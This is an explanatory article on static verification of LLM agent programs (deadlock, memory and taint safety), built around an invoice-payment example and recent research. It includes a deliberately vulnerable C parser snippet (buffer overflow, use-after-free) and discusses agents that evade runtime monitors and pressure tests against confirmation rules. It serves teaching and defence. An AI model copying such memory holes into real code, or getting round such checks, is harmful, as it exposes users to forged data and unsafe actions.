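# What static proofs of deadlock freedom, memory safety and taint safety establish about agent programs

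## What is an agent program, and what can be proved about it before it runs?

An agent program is software that calls a language model, passes data between the model and a set of outside functions (its tools), and uses those tools to act on the world, for example by sending an email, editing a file or paying a bill. Static verification examines such a program before it runs and aims to prove that no run can produce a precisely defined kind of error. Deadlock freedom means that programs never end up all waiting for one another forever. Memory safety means that a program never reads or writes memory it has no right to use at that moment. Taint safety means that untrusted data never influences a sensitive operation without a check in between; a "tainted" value is one marked as possibly depending on untrusted data. Programmers had ways of ruling out all three kinds of error long before language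 models existed, but models add a difficulty because nobody can tell in advance what they will return.

### An invoice assistant and its parts

A small company might use an agent program to pay its bills. The program runs three agents concurrently. The Reader fetches emails with PDF attachments and uses a model to extract the payee, account and amount. The Clerk keeps a ledger, and the Payer sends the money.

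```
 1  Reader:  mail = fetch_mail()
 2           text = parse_pdf(mail.attachment)
 3           inv: Invoice = model("Extract payee, account, amount", text)
 4           send inv to Clerk
 5  Clerk:   receive inv from Reader
 6           ledger.add(inv)
 7           send inv to Payer
 8           receive receipt from Payer
 9  Payer:   receive inv from Clerk
10           receipt = send_payment(inv.account, inv.amount)
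11           send receipt to Clerk
```

Each agent repeats its own lines while the assistant is switched on. A `send` puts a message in a queue and carries on, while a `receive` waits until a message is there. `Invoice` is a record that holds the payee and account as text and the amount as a number.

Line 3 is the model call. Almost everything else belongs to the harness, the ordinary software around the model that builds its input, reads its output and carries out its tool calls. The harness also includes code the listing leaves out, such as the library that runs the three loops and turns the model's text into an `Invoice`. The tools are `fetch_mail`, `parse_pdf` and `send_payment`, and the ledger is stored state that persists across invoices. Real agents are rarely this compact. *Agents as Software* (Barke and Murali, 2026) points out that the "program" is scattered across prompts, tools,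 memories and workflows.

In the invoice assistant, code fixes the order of the steps and the model only fills in three fields. In many other agents, the model gets a list of tools and picks the next call at every turn. *LLM-as-Code* (2026) argues against that design, using the example of an agent that fetches a list of web pages. A `for` loop over the list runs exactly once for each page. A model in charge of the loop may fetch the first page again, leave out the fifth or stop early, because it samples each decision from a probability distribution. A better model makes these errors rarer but cannot rule them out. The choice of design also affects what can be proved. If the model picked the tools in the invoice assistant, an analyser would have to allow for a payment at any turn, even before the Clerk had seen anything.

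### What an analyser can read

Agent programs give an analyser three quite different kinds of text to work on. The simplest is a fixed workflow like the listing above. *Provable Coordination for LLM Agents via Message Sequence Charts* (Bollig, Függer and Nowak, 2026) presents a small language for such workflows, in which one text describes the messages among all the agents. Model calls, tool calls and human decisions appear in it as opaque functions, whose input and output types are known but whose contents are not. In the paper's introductory example, a Planner writes a plan and decides whether a human Reviewer has to see it, an Executor carries it out, and an Orchestrator collects the results. The text specifies who sends what to whom and who decides on each branch, but not what the plan contains. *λ_A* (2026) interprets developers' existing configuration files as typed programs and reports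 real bugs that existing frameworks had missed.

Some agents write a new program for each task, so the program to check is the one the model has just written. In *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026), the model writes Haskell, whose types record what effects code may have on the outside world. The harness checks the program against an expected type, returns any type error to the model for another try, and runs the program only once it passes. The paper's smallest example is a calculator whose answer must have the type "integer". If a user asks it to delete all files on the server and then compute a factorial, the model may well write that program, but it never runs because code that touches files does not have the type "integer". Here "before it runs" means after the model writes the program and before the harness executes it, while the rest of the agent is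 already running.

The third text is the source code of the framework on which developers build their agents. In *Containment Verification* (2026), Moon and Varshney verified PocketFlow, a minimalist framework that represents workflows as graphs. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) proves theorems about the interpreter that calls the model, so the theorems hold for every agent written in its language. Work at this level benefits many applications. But a framework has no built-in concept of ledgers or suppliers, so the proof covers a rule about them only if somebody writes that rule into the specification, the exact statement of what the proof is to show.

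### Reasoning about all runs at once

The invoice assistant has too many possible runs to list, because the run changes with each email, each PDF, each answer from the model and the order in which the three agents take their turns. Static analysis therefore replaces exact values with coarse descriptions and follows those descriptions through the code.

To prove that `send_payment` never receives a negative amount, the analyser can track the amount's possible signs and ignore its exact value. After line 3 the amount may have any sign, because the model may have returned any number, and this is still true at line 10. The analyser therefore reports a possible violation, which a credit note in the mail could indeed cause. If the developer then makes the Payer skip every invoice with a negative amount, the analyser finds that the amount at line 10 can only be zero or positive, which proves the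 property for every possible mail.

Let $R$ be the set of runs that the program can have and $R'$ the set of runs that fit the coarse descriptions. The analyser's rules ensure that $R \subseteq R'$, or in other words $R'$ over-approximates $R$. If $R'$ contains no faulty run, neither does $R$. An analysis that keeps to this discipline is sound: it never declares a program free of a fault that some modelled run has. ("Modelled" carries weight in that definition, since $R$ contains only what the analyser's account of the language and the tools allows for.)

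A faulty run in $R'$ does not prove that the program is faulty, because $R'$ may contain runs that the program can never have. The analyser then raises a false alarm. Suppose the Payer sets a flag `refund` whenever the amount is below zero, and a few lines later pays only if the flag is off. No run pays a negative amount. But an analyser that records the sign and the flag separately loses the connection between them. At the payment, it records that the flag is off and the amount may have any sign, so it reports a possible negative payment. A finer analyser would track the connection, using more computation, but would still raise a false alarm on some other program.

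That last claim is a theorem. Henry Gordon Rice proved in 1953 that no algorithm can decide, for every program, whether the program's behaviour has a given property, unless all programs have the property or none do. To see why this holds for the negative payment, take any program $Q$ that makes no payments and add a final line that pays minus one euro. The new program makes a negative payment exactly when $Q$ finishes. A checker that always answered and was always right could therefore decide whether an arbitrary program finishes, which Alan Turing showed in 1936 that no algorithm can do. So every automatic checker that always answers is wrong about some programs. A sound one never passes a bad program, so it must reject some good ones.

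One way to deal with this is to restrict the language, as Bollig and colleagues do. Developers can't write some programs, but every well-typed workflow is free of deadlock. Another is to leave some checks until the program runs. A programming-languages textbook at Northeastern University calls a language "statically safe" if it performs as many checks as possible in advance and leaves only the undecidable ones for later. The file library of Zhou and colleagues divides its checks this way. The type checker rejects a program that names a file by a plain string, and the library checks during the run whether a permitted path leads out of its folder through a symbolic link, because that depends on the disk.

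One can also accept the rejections. Erik Meijer, who proposed in ACM Queue that agents should have to prove their planned actions safe, argued in a talk for IT Revolution that a wrongly refused action does society much less harm than an unsafe one, and that the harness can discard the plan and request another. That seems right for a program that a model has just written, but less so for a framework that people maintain by hand, where an engineer spends an afternoon on each false alarm.

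### Testing and monitoring

A test runs the program on chosen inputs and checks the outcome. Paying a thousand invoices correctly doesn't prove that the next one will be paid correctly, and with a model in the loop, even repeating the same test can produce a different outcome. Moon and Varshney rank guarantees by the scenarios they cover. The lowest guarantees hold for the inputs somebody tried, the next for an assumed distribution of inputs, and the highest for every value the model could emit. The ranking is fair, but it doesn't measure how much a guarantee establishes about each scenario. A test can compare the extracted amount with the amount printed on the PDF, which none of the proofs discussed here can do.

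A monitor checks an agent's actions during the actual run and intervenes. Barke and Murali describe one for a shop's agent that tries to issue a refund. The monitor has recorded from an earlier tool call that the customer has not shipped the item back, so it blocks the refund, and the agent then asks for confirmation of the return. Static analysis of the same agent would check whether any path leads to the refund before there is evidence of the return, and a warning would mean only that the configuration permits a bad run. Because the monitor has access to actual values, it does not need the coarse descriptions used in static analysis and avoids many of the false alarms. But it detects problems late, perhaps when half the task is already done, and it provides no information about runs that have not happened.

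*Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026) reviews 38 studies and finds that monitoring is the most mature way to enforce rules on agents, with guarantees that cover single steps or short stretches of a run. In one of those studies, enforcement blocked 94% of unsafe actions, yet in most settings the agents completed fewer than 5% of their tasks both safely and correctly, because they found other unsafe routes. This result comes from a single study of one kind of agent, and the review gives seven of its nine main claims the lowest grade of certainty. Still, it is a reason to want guarantees about whole runs.

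### A model that may return anything

The model has caused little difficulty so far because the sign analysis implicitly assumed the worst about its output. No one has a description of a large language model from which one could prove that it copies account numbers correctly. The proofs therefore over-approximate the model too, as coarsely as possible, by treating the call as a function that may return any value of its declared type. For line 3, the call may return any payee, any account and any amount.

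Moon and Varshney declare the model as a method with a return type and no body in Dafny, a programming language with a built-in proof checker. Dafny accepts a proof about the surrounding code only if the proof works for every value of that type. A real model returns some value of the type, whatever its training, so the proof covers its runs. This includes runs under prompt injection, where an attacker places text in the data that the model follows as an instruction. Zhou and colleagues assume an arbitrary computable function from prompts to programs. *Provably Auditable and Safe LLM Agents from Human-Authored Ontologies* (2026) goes further and puts everything unpredictable into one arbitrary sequence, from which a run draws its model outputs, random numbers, clock times, human decisions and the order in which agents take turns.

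The resulting theorems share a form:

$$A \;\Rightarrow\; \forall \omega \in \Omega \;\; \forall r \in \mathrm{Runs}(\omega) : \; r \models P$$

Here $\omega$ is a sequence of model outputs, $\Omega$ is the set of all sequences that the types permit, $\mathrm{Runs}(\omega)$ is the set of runs that the program can have with those outputs, $P$ is the property, and $A$ is the list of assumptions. The formula means that if $A$ holds, every run satisfies $P$, whichever sequence in $\Omega$ the model returns.

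Moon and Varshney prove such a result by describing the framework twice, as a simple abstract machine and as a detailed one close to the code. First they prove that the abstract machine obeys the policy whatever sequence of actions the model emits. Then they prove that the two machines start in matching states, that every step of the detailed machine has a matching abstract step with the same action, and that the detailed step obeys the policy if the abstract one does. By induction, every run of the detailed machine matches a run of the abstract one and therefore obeys the policy. To apply the result to a deployed agent, they must also assume that every effect on the outside world passes through the interface they modelled. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) similarly assumes that its runtime can intercept every tool call. For the invoice assistant, $A$ would be the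 assumption that money leaves the company only through line 10 and that the harness rejects any model output that is not a proper `Invoice`.

The usefulness of such a theorem depends heavily on the declared type. If the account is declared as text, no proof can show that the company pays only its suppliers, since any account number is text. If the type is instead "an entry in the supplier list" and the harness refuses everything else, the property follows directly. The proof still can't show that the payment goes to the right supplier or is for the right amount. Bollig and colleagues likewise guarantee the coordination, but not that model outputs are correct or that the task succeeds.

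*Can Formal Methods Apply to Agent Security?*, a practitioner's blog post, warns that if the proof lets the model return any string, a failed proof may come with an example run that no real model would produce, and that such a run is hard to tell from a true design flaw. This concern matters little for line 3, because anyone can mail the company a PDF and attackers choose their words deliberately. It matters more for a model call that sees only the company's own data.

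### Which kind of property

A safety property says that something bad never happens, and a finite part of a run is enough to show a violation. An example is "No payment leaves before the ledger has the invoice." (Dantas and colleagues use the term more broadly, for any temporal logic formula that a finished plan satisfies or fails.) Memory safety is a safety property because each violation is a single memory access. Taint safety is also one if the record of a run includes the taint marks. It is violated when a tainted value reaches a sink, an operation that untrusted data must not control, without having passed an approved check. The invoice assistant as it stands violates taint safety at line 10.

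Taint safety is often a stand-in for noninterference, a stronger property under which changing the untrusted inputs cannot change what trusted observers see. No single run can refute noninterference, so one has to compare two runs with the same trusted inputs and different mail. If the model is allowed to answer arbitrarily, its answers could differ between the two runs even where the mail had no influence, and the proof would fail for every program that shows a model's output to anyone. Zhou and colleagues avoid this by treating the model as a function, so that equal prompts get equal answers. *The LLMbda Calculus* proves a probabilistic version of noninterference, which suits a model that samples its answers, and the proof is checked by the proof assistant Lean. The theorem is "termination-insensitive", meaning that it disregards what an observer could learn from whether the program finishes.

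A liveness property is a claim that something good eventually happens, for example that the company eventually pays every valid invoice. No finite part of a run can refute such a claim, because the payment might still come. Liveness is hard to prove when the model may return anything. If the Reader repeats its question until the model returns a positive amount, the model may return minus one forever. With a limit of five attempts, one can prove that the loop ends, provided the model service answers each time, but not that the company pays, because the model may return minus one all five times and leave the invoice unpaid. Zhou and colleagues include a similar limit in their formal account, which restricts how deeply agents can call other agents.

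Deadlock freedom is a safety property. It rules out any state in which every process in some group is waiting for another process in that group. Swapping lines 7 and 8 would cause a deadlock on the first invoice, because the Clerk would wait for a receipt before handing over the invoice, and the Payer would wait for the invoice before issuing a receipt. Bollig and colleagues define deadlock freedom as the requirement that every partial execution can continue to a complete one. This does not require the agents to finish, so a loop that could end at any time but never does would pass.

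## How is deadlock among agents ruled out, and what can still go wrong when it is?

Swapping two lines of the invoice assistant made the Clerk and the Payer wait for each other forever. In larger agent programs, deadlocks also arise over things that agents share, such as a file, a test server or a ledger. Programmers protect a shared thing with a lock, which only one agent can hold at a time while the others wait. Suppose the invoice assistant's ledger has a lock. The Clerk holds the lock from when it enters an invoice until it marks the invoice as paid, and the Payer takes the lock to check that nobody has already paid the invoice.

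```
Clerk:   receive inv from Reader
         acquire ledger
         ledger.add(inv)
         send inv to Payer
         receive receipt from Payer
         ledger.mark_paid(inv)
         release ledger
Payer:   receive inv from Clerk
         acquire ledger
         check that inv is unpaid
         receipt = send_payment(inv.account, inv.amount)
         release ledger
         send receipt to Clerk
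```

The Clerk and the Payer both stop at the first invoice. The Clerk holds the lock while it waits for the receipt, which the Payer can't issue without the lock. The Reader is not involved and keeps filling the Clerk's queue, so the assistant still looks busy from outside.

### Four conditions and a cycle

In 1971 Edward Coffman, Michael Elphick and Arie Shoshani listed four conditions that hold in every deadlock over resources, and all four hold here. Only one agent at a time can have the ledger lock (mutual exclusion). The Clerk keeps the lock while it waits for something else (hold and wait). The harness never takes a lock away from an agent (no preemption). The agents wait for one another in a circle (circular wait). A design that makes any one of these conditions impossible prevents this kind of deadlock.

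The circle is easiest to see in a wait-for graph, which has a node for each agent and an arrow from one agent to another if the first waits for something that only the second can supply. In the example, one arrow runs from the Clerk to the Payer, for the receipt, and another runs from the Payer back to the Clerk, for the lock. As long as each waiting agent needs one particular thing from one particular agent, there is a deadlock exactly when the graph has a cycle. (If an agent would accept a message from any of several others, a cycle is not enough, because an agent outside the cycle may free it.)

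The usual way to prevent cycles is to rank the resources and let an agent wait only for something that ranks above everything it already holds. Suppose there were a cycle anyway, in which agent $a_i$ waits for resource $r_i$ and the next agent, $a_{i+1}$, holds it. Since $a_{i+1}$ holds $r_i$ and waits for $r_{i+1}$, the rule gives $\mathrm{rank}(r_i) < \mathrm{rank}(r_{i+1})$. Going once round a cycle of $k$ agents, one gets

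$$\mathrm{rank}(r_1) < \mathrm{rank}(r_2) < \dots < \mathrm{rank}(r_k) < \mathrm{rank}(r_1),$$

which is impossible.

To apply this to the invoice assistant, we can treat the receipt as something the Payer holds from the moment the Clerk sends the invoice, and rank it below the ledger lock. The Payer may then wait for the lock while it owes a receipt, but the Clerk may not wait for the receipt while it holds the lock. So the Clerk has to release the lock after entering the invoice and take it again to mark the invoice as paid. This removes the deadlock, but it also lets other agents read the ledger after the money has left and before the Clerk has recorded the payment.

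### Deadlock among language models

The ledger deadlock happens on every run, so the first test would reveal it, but most deadlocks depend on timing. The textbook case is Edsger Dijkstra's dining philosophers, who sit round a table with one fork between each pair of neighbours and need both adjacent forks to eat. If they all pick up their left forks at the same moment, nobody can eat.

*DPBench* (Hasan and BusiReddyGari, 2026) has language models play the dining philosophers. Each episode has five copies of one model and lasts at most 30 steps. At every step, each copy sees its two forks and chooses to grab the left one, grab the right one, release what it holds or wait. When all copies chose simultaneously, without messages and with a neutral prompt, GPT-5.2 deadlocked in 25% of episodes, Claude Opus 4.5 in 55%, Grok 4.1 in 70%, Llama 4 Maverick in 77% and Gemini 2.5 Flash in 90%. Players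 that chose at random deadlocked in only 13%. This makes sense, because identical models that see the same thing tend to make the same move, and random choices break that symmetry.

The experimenters then varied the set-up while keeping the same model, Google's Gemini 2.5 Flash (released in 2025), and ran 20 or 30 episodes of each variant.

| Change to the set-up | Deadlock rate | 95% interval |
|---|---|---|
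| None | 90% | 74–97% |
| Prompt that states no goal | 100% | 84–100% |
| One round of messages before each move | 87% | 70–95% |
| Three rounds of messages | 0% | 0–16% |
| Five rounds of messages | 5% | 1–24% |
| Prompt to think about what the others will do | 5% | 1–24% |
| Prompt to wait a turn or two at random | 0% | 0–16% |
| Prompt that fixes which fork to grab first | 0% | 0–16% |
| Ten philosophers instead of five | 10% | 4–26% |

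The prompt about fork order tells even-numbered philosophers to start with the right fork and odd-numbered ones with the left, which provably prevents deadlock if they obey. If all five forks are taken and nobody has two, then either everyone holds the left fork or everyone holds the right one, and neither can happen under this rule. The experiment shows only that Gemini obeyed well enough in 20 episodes. Three rounds of messages worked as well but took four to five times as many model calls.

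Hasan and BusiReddyGari go too far in concluding that the protocol, not the model's capability, decides the outcome. Under the same protocol, their five models had deadlock rates from 25% to 90%, and they tried the prompts and message rounds in the table only on Gemini. Their rates also include episodes that are not strictly deadlocks. The benchmark counts a deadlock as soon as each philosopher holds one fork, even though they could still put a fork down, and it also counts episodes that run out of time. When the philosophers moved one after another, Claude Opus 4.5 still "deadlocked" in 60% of episodes, mostly because it waited so often that time ran out. All five models date from 2025, so the exact rates may not carry over to current models.

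### One global text, projected onto each agent

A prompt makes deadlock rarer. To exclude it, Bollig and colleagues do away with separately written agent programs. The developer writes one text for all agents, and a compiler derives each agent's program from it. In their notation, the original invoice assistant looks roughly like this:

```
act Reader: inv = read_invoice()
msg Reader(inv) -> Clerk(inv)
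act Clerk:  entry = ledger_add(inv)
msg Clerk(inv) -> Payer(inv)
act Payer:  receipt = send_payment(inv)
msg Payer(receipt) -> Clerk(receipt)
```

The derivation, called projection, goes through the text line by line. A `msg` line becomes a send in the sender's program, a receive in the receiver's program and nothing in the other agents' programs. An `act` line goes into the program of the agent it names. The Clerk's program therefore receives the invoice, adds it to the ledger, sends it on and receives the receipt.

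No global text can produce the version with the Clerk's two lines swapped, because whichever of the two `msg` lines between the Clerk and the Payer comes first in the text comes first for both agents. The shared order also prevents deadlock in longer texts. At any moment before the text is finished, there is an earliest line that some agent has yet to finish, and every agent has finished the lines above it. If it is an `act` line, its agent can carry it out. If it is a `msg` line, the sender can send, because sending never blocks. Once the message is in the queue, the receiver can take it, because both agents work through the messages between them in the same order. So some agent can always proceed until the text is finished.

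The full proof has to handle cases where some agents have started later parts of the text before others have finished earlier ones. Its central step, the "Zipper lemma", states that the agents can always complete the earlier part in a way that fits the later work already done. The proof assistant Lean has checked it.

An agent that makes a decision must tell the other agents whose actions depend on it. Suppose a Manager has to approve invoices that the Clerk considers large. Without a message from the Clerk, the Payer cannot tell which invoices these are, so it might wait for an approval that never comes. In the language of Bollig and colleagues, every `if` and `while` names the agent that decides, and that agent's projected program sends "true" or "false" to all other agents that occur in either branch. In a loop, it does so on every round. These control messages carry a tag of a type that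 ordinary data cannot have, so model output cannot be mistaken for one. With $n$ agents, each decision adds at most $n-1$ messages.

The theorem covers only messages. The language has no locks, and an action is a function that returns a value. If `ledger_add` took the ledger lock and a later action released it, the deadlock from the beginning of this section could occur in a workflow that the compiler accepts. The theorem also assumes that every loop ends, and Bollig and colleagues leave for future work the case where a model call never returns.

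A model can also write the global text, and any workflow the compiler accepts is still guaranteed free of deadlock. In a small experiment with arithmetic tasks, the compiler accepted all ten workflows that GPT-4.1 wrote on the first attempt. All ten finished, but four returned the wrong number because they misapplied a rule about division by zero.

### A type for each channel, and a gate for the model

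Session types reach a similar goal from the other direction, by giving each end of a channel a type that describes the conversation on it. With `!` for sending and `?` for receiving, the channel between the Clerk and the Payer has these two ends:

$$\text{Clerk: } \; !\mathrm{Invoice}.\,?\mathrm{Receipt}.\,\mathrm{end} \qquad\quad \text{Payer: } \; ?\mathrm{Invoice}.\,!\mathrm{Receipt}.\,\mathrm{end}$$

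The type checker requires that the two types mirror each other and that each program follows its own type. Whenever one side expects a message on this channel, it is the other side's turn to send one. The swapped Clerk would have the type $?\mathrm{Receipt}.\,!\mathrm{Invoice}.\,\mathrm{end}$, which does not mirror the Payer's, so the checker rejects it.

Checking each channel separately misses cycles that run through several channels or through a lock. In the ledger deadlock, both agents follow their types, but the Payer never reaches its send. Multiparty session types handle cycles across channels by deriving all the local types from one global protocol, much as projection does. They reject some protocols that Bollig and colleagues accept, because they require an agent that isn't told about a decision to behave consistently in both branches.

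If a model chooses each next step, a type checker has no program to check. *Concordat* (Sikaroudi, 2026) therefore enforces the protocol while the agent runs. Its Python library describes one agent's permitted behaviour as a set of states, each with its own legal tools. For the Payer, the state "received" might offer only the check that the invoice is unpaid, "checked" might offer only the payment, and "paid" would be final. On every turn, the harness shows the model only the current state's tools. If the model names another tool anyway, the harness returns an error message and does not run the tool. The harness also allows only one tool call at a time, so that each call starts from the state the previous one left.

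Sikaroudi tested this on 50 airline tasks from τ-bench, a benchmark for customer-service agents. The airline's rules require an explicit "yes" from the customer before any change to a booking, and he made the simulated customers push back with "just do it and stop asking". An ordinary agent, which had the rule only in its prompt, made changes without a "yes" in 13 of 50 runs with GPT-4.1 and in 29 of 128 runs with Claude Haiku 5.5. The Concordat agent made none, which follows from the design because the gate and the measurement use the same keyword test for "yes". The more informative result is that the gate had little effect on task completion. With GPT-4.1, the Concordat agent completed 22 tasks and the ordinary agent 20. With Haiku, they completed 105 and 112. Neither difference is statistically significant.

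For deadlock, however, Concordat proves less than its subtitle, "Typed Sessions for LLM Agents", might suggest. When a developer defines a protocol, the library checks that every state has some path to a final state, which rules out dead ends within a single agent. It does not compare the protocols of different agents, so two agents could each be stuck waiting for the other even though both protocols pass the check.

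Waites (2026), in *A Typed Language for Agent Coordination*, presents plumbing, a language that types the connections between agents. Its compiler accepts a network of agents only if every output fits the input it feeds. Waites says the compiler also checks "within limits for deadlocks" but does not specify the limits. Type checks alone would not keep a network from getting stuck, because the language has a "barrier" that waits for one value from each of two streams. If one of the two agents feeding it never produces a value, everything after the barrier waits forever.

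### Visiting every state

A model checker, which visits every state a protocol can reach, can treat locks and messages together. *TraceFix* (Xia, Li and colleagues, 2026) uses the model checker TLC on protocols written in the specification language TLA+. A state records how far each agent has got, which messages are in each queue and which agent holds each lock. TLC starts from the initial state, computes every state that one step of any agent can lead to, repeats this for each new state, and stops when it finds no more. If it finds a state in which no agent can move although some have not finished, it prints the steps that led there.

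Xia and colleagues illustrate this with a developer agent that locks the code repository and then the build server, and a testing agent that locks them in the opposite order. If each agent takes its first lock, then its second, then releases both and stops, it has four possible positions, and the two agents together have 16 combinations. Three of these are impossible because both agents would hold the same lock. One of the remaining 13 is a deadlock, where each agent holds its first lock and waits for the other's. A test reaches the deadlock only if both agents take their first lock before either takes its second, but TLC always reaches it. In the repaired version, neither agent needs the other's lock, though having both agents take the locks in the same order would also have worked.

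In TraceFix, Claude Opus 4.6 writes the protocol from a task description and uses TLC's trace to repair it whenever the check fails. Where an agent must make a decision during the run, the protocol lists the options and TLC checks all of them, on the assumption that a model may give any answer. On 48 tasks with three to seven agents, 30 protocols passed the first check and the rest passed after at most four repairs. Deadlocks prompted 20 of the 29 repair attempts. Protocols for tasks that involved only locks never needed repair, probably because the model uses the standard technique of acquiring them in a fixed order. The largest protocol had 7.7 million states, and no check took longer than a minute.

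The search is exhaustive only within bounds. The number of agents is fixed, so a protocol that passes with three reviewers may fail with four. Queues hold at most three messages by default, but this limit matters little because TLC reports any protocol that would exceed it as faulty. A bigger problem arises when TLC runs out of time. The repair then sometimes simplifies the protocol's retries while the real agents go on retrying as before, so the check covers less than what runs. Xia and colleagues also deliberately leave out all liveness properties, because many legitimate workflows let a reviewer reject a draft any number of times.

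Agents running verified protocols can still get stuck. The harness put each agent's part into its prompt, and a monitor rejected messages on undeclared channels and requests for undeclared locks. With GPT-5-mini, 8.8% of 432 runs still ended in deadlock or livelock (agents that keep acting without making progress). The proof covers only the protocol, and the models sometimes departed from its order of steps, which the monitor does not check. Verification still helped in a separate comparison on 15 tasks with the same monitor, where 31.1% of runs got stuck with unverified protocols and 14.1% with verified ones.

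A stricter design, in which a mediator handled all locks and messages for the agents, lowered the share of stuck runs further, to 4.5%. But the agents met all their objectives in only 44.7% of runs, compared with 81.5% with the monitor, because the mediator could not adapt when a tool failed. The implementation by Bollig and colleagues resembles the mediator in that the harness itself executes each projected program and calls the model only inside actions, so the model cannot reorder the steps or improvise.

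### Agents that never finish without being deadlocked

A group of agents can fail to finish in several ways that no deadlock check detects. In a livelock, the agents keep reacting to one another without making progress. If the dining philosophers all keep picking up their left forks and putting them down again, none of them ever eats, although each can always act. In starvation, one participant waits indefinitely while the others continue. If the Payer always takes the most urgent invoice first and urgent ones keep arriving, an ordinary invoice may never be processed.

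A call that never returns can block agents as a deadlock does. If the bank's server accepts the payment request but never replies, the Payer waits for the bank and the Clerk waits for the Payer. The bank waits for nobody, so the wait-for graph has no cycle, and reordering locks or messages would not help. The usual remedy is a time limit, but when it expires, the Payer does not know whether the money has been sent.

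Even a single agent can loop endlessly. In *When Agents Do Not Stop*, Hou, Wang and colleagues (2026) looked for "infinite agentic loops", in which a program can repeat model calls, tool calls or handovers between agents without an effective limit. In a project called LiteRAG, for example, a planner asks a model for a plan until the answer can be parsed and passes a check, with no limit on the number of attempts. In an assistant published by NVIDIA, an empty answer makes the program append "Respond with a real output." to the conversation and call the model again, so the conversation grows with each round. Both loops can end, but whether they do depends on the model's output, as with the Reader that asks again until it gets a positive amount.

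IAL-Scan uses a project's source code and the known behaviour of eight agent frameworks to build a graph of calls, transitions and retries. It searches the graph for cycles that contain costly steps and checks whether a limit covers the whole cycle. A cap of ten turns on an inner agent does not prevent endless execution if an outer loop can keep restarting that agent. The static analysis found 340 candidates in 6,549 public projects. A language model reduced them to 74, and human reviewers confirmed 68 of these, in 47 projects.

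The reviewers found these 68 flaws by reading code, without observing any runaway execution. The number is also a lower bound. The reviewers found seven loops that the tool had missed, and when they repeated the filtering twice with the same language model, it kept only 64 and then 60 of the 68. IAL-Scan can therefore find faults, but the absence of a warning does not prove that a project's loops terminate.

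### Stale reads and reordered effects

Agents can also finish on time and still get in one another's way. Khan (2026), in *Verified Detection and Prevention of Concurrency Anomalies*, describes an agent's operation as a read of shared data, a model call that may take seconds or minutes, and a write. During the model call, other agents can change what the agent has read. In his example, a flight agent reads that a trip starts on 14 June and begins to draft the booking. Meanwhile the user moves the trip to 21 June, and the agent then books the 14th. He calls this a stale generation. Operation $i$ suffers from it if another agent's operation $j$ writes to a cell $c$ that $i$ has read, such that

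$$\mathrm{read\_time}_i < \mathrm{write\_time}_j < \mathrm{write\_time}_i \quad\text{and}\quad \mathrm{read}_i(c) \neq \mathrm{written}_j(c).$$

The repair of the ledger deadlock made such a case possible. Suppose a fourth agent drafts a cash forecast from the ledger. It can now read an invoice as unpaid just after the Payer has sent the money. While its model is writing the forecast, the Clerk marks the invoice as paid, and the finished forecast counts the same money again. No agent ever waits for another, so every deadlock check passes.

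Khan defines three further anomalies in the same style. In a "phantom tool", somebody removes a tool after the agent chooses it but before the agent calls it. In a "causal cascade", an agent builds on a result that its author later withdraws, as when the Clerk cancels an entry that the Payer has already acted on. In "tool-effect reordering", the effects of one operation happen in a different order from the one the agent intended. If the Payer wants to send the money and then email the supplier, the email may go out first and announce a payment that then fails. Khan demonstrates this reordering on LangGraph, a widely used agent framework, and reproduces a related fault in ByteDance's deer-flow, where one update silently overwrites another.

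It is still unclear how common these anomalies are. In Khan's tests with GPT-4o, stale generations occurred in 1%, 35% and 100% of sessions for three kinds of task, but he had designed the 1% and 100% tasks to produce those results. Stale reads also don't always matter. He found that the share of them in which fresh data would have changed the agent's decision ranged from 0% to 100%, depending on the agent's role.

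The obvious protection against stale generations is to hold a lock from the read to the write. In Khan's measurements, this raised costs by a factor of up to 1.6 with GPT-4o and 2.3 with Claude Sonnet 4.5. It also makes agents keep locks during long model calls, and once an agent needs two locks, hold-and-wait becomes possible again and the locks need an order. Alternatively, an agent can hold no lock while its model works, check before the write whether its data have changed, and repeat the model call if they have. This added about 8% to the token count in one of Khan's workloads and nothing measurable in the others. However, an agent whose data keep changing may have to start over repeatedly, which is a form of starvation. Starting over is also safe only if the operation has had no outside effects, such as a payment, which the harness cannot reverse.

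## What does memory safety mean for an agent program?

A proof about locks assumes that a lock changes only when an agent acquires or releases it. In a language such as C, a faulty line anywhere in the process can break that assumption by overwriting the bytes that hold the lock. A memory-safe program has no such lines, because it reads and writes only memory it is allowed to use at that moment.

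### Out of bounds and after free

Suppose `parse_pdf`, the invoice assistant's PDF parser, is a C library that runs in the same process as the harness. It writes the payee's name into a record that has 32 bytes for the name, then a one-byte mark that is 1 if the record depends on untrusted data.

```
struct field { char name[32]; char tainted; };

n = read_length(pdf);
for (i = 0; i < n; i++)
    f->name[i] = read_byte(pdf);
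```

The length `n` comes from the file, and the loop never compares it with 32. If an attacker mails a PDF that gives the length as 33, the last iteration of the loop writes to `name[32]`, one byte past the end of the name, where the mark is stored. This is a spatial error, an access outside the bounds of an object. C normally doesn't check for this, so the program continues without reporting an error.

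A temporal error uses a valid address at the wrong time:

```
page = malloc(4096);
read_page(pdf, page);
free(page);
title = find_title(page);
```

After `free`, the allocator may give the same 4,096 bytes to another part of the program, perhaps for the next supplier's invoice. `find_title` then returns a title from the wrong document. This temporal error is called a "use after free". Freeing the same memory twice is also a temporal error.

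### Why the other proofs depend on it

If the 33rd byte in the attacker's PDF is zero, the record counts as trusted, and a check in front of `send_payment` lets it through. An analyser that follows taint through the source code would miss this because no line assigns to `tainted`. Leaving the taint marks out of the running program doesn't help either, because a longer name could overwrite an account number from the supplier list, and the analyser's proof would still count that number as trusted.

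Deadlock proofs are equally vulnerable to memory errors. If a stray write marks the ledger lock as taken, every agent that requests it waits for a holder that doesn't exist. If the write marks a held lock as free, two agents can hold it at once. A proof about taint or deadlock therefore has to assume that all code in the process is memory safe, and this assumption is part of the trusted computing base (everything that must work correctly for the proof to hold of the running system).

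Developers can rely less on that assumption by running the parser in a separate process. The operating system then stops the parser from writing to the harness's memory. A memory error can still crash the parser or corrupt its output, but the harness should treat text from an outside PDF as untrusted anyway.

### Safety from the language

Python, JavaScript and Java prevent both kinds of error with garbage collection and bounds checks. A program in these languages cannot invent an address. It gets a reference only by creating an object or receiving the reference from elsewhere. The garbage collector frees an object only when the program can no longer reach it, which prevents temporal errors. To prevent spatial errors, the runtime compares every index with the length of the array. In Python and Java, writing the 33rd byte raises an exception. The exception may stop the Reader, but that is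 a much safer failure than a forged taint mark. JavaScript enlarges an ordinary array to make room and ignores the write if the array is a typed array, whose length is fixed, so the byte never lands in another object. These guarantees come from the rules of the language, not from a proof about the individual program, and they hold only if the interpreter and the collector implement those rules correctly.

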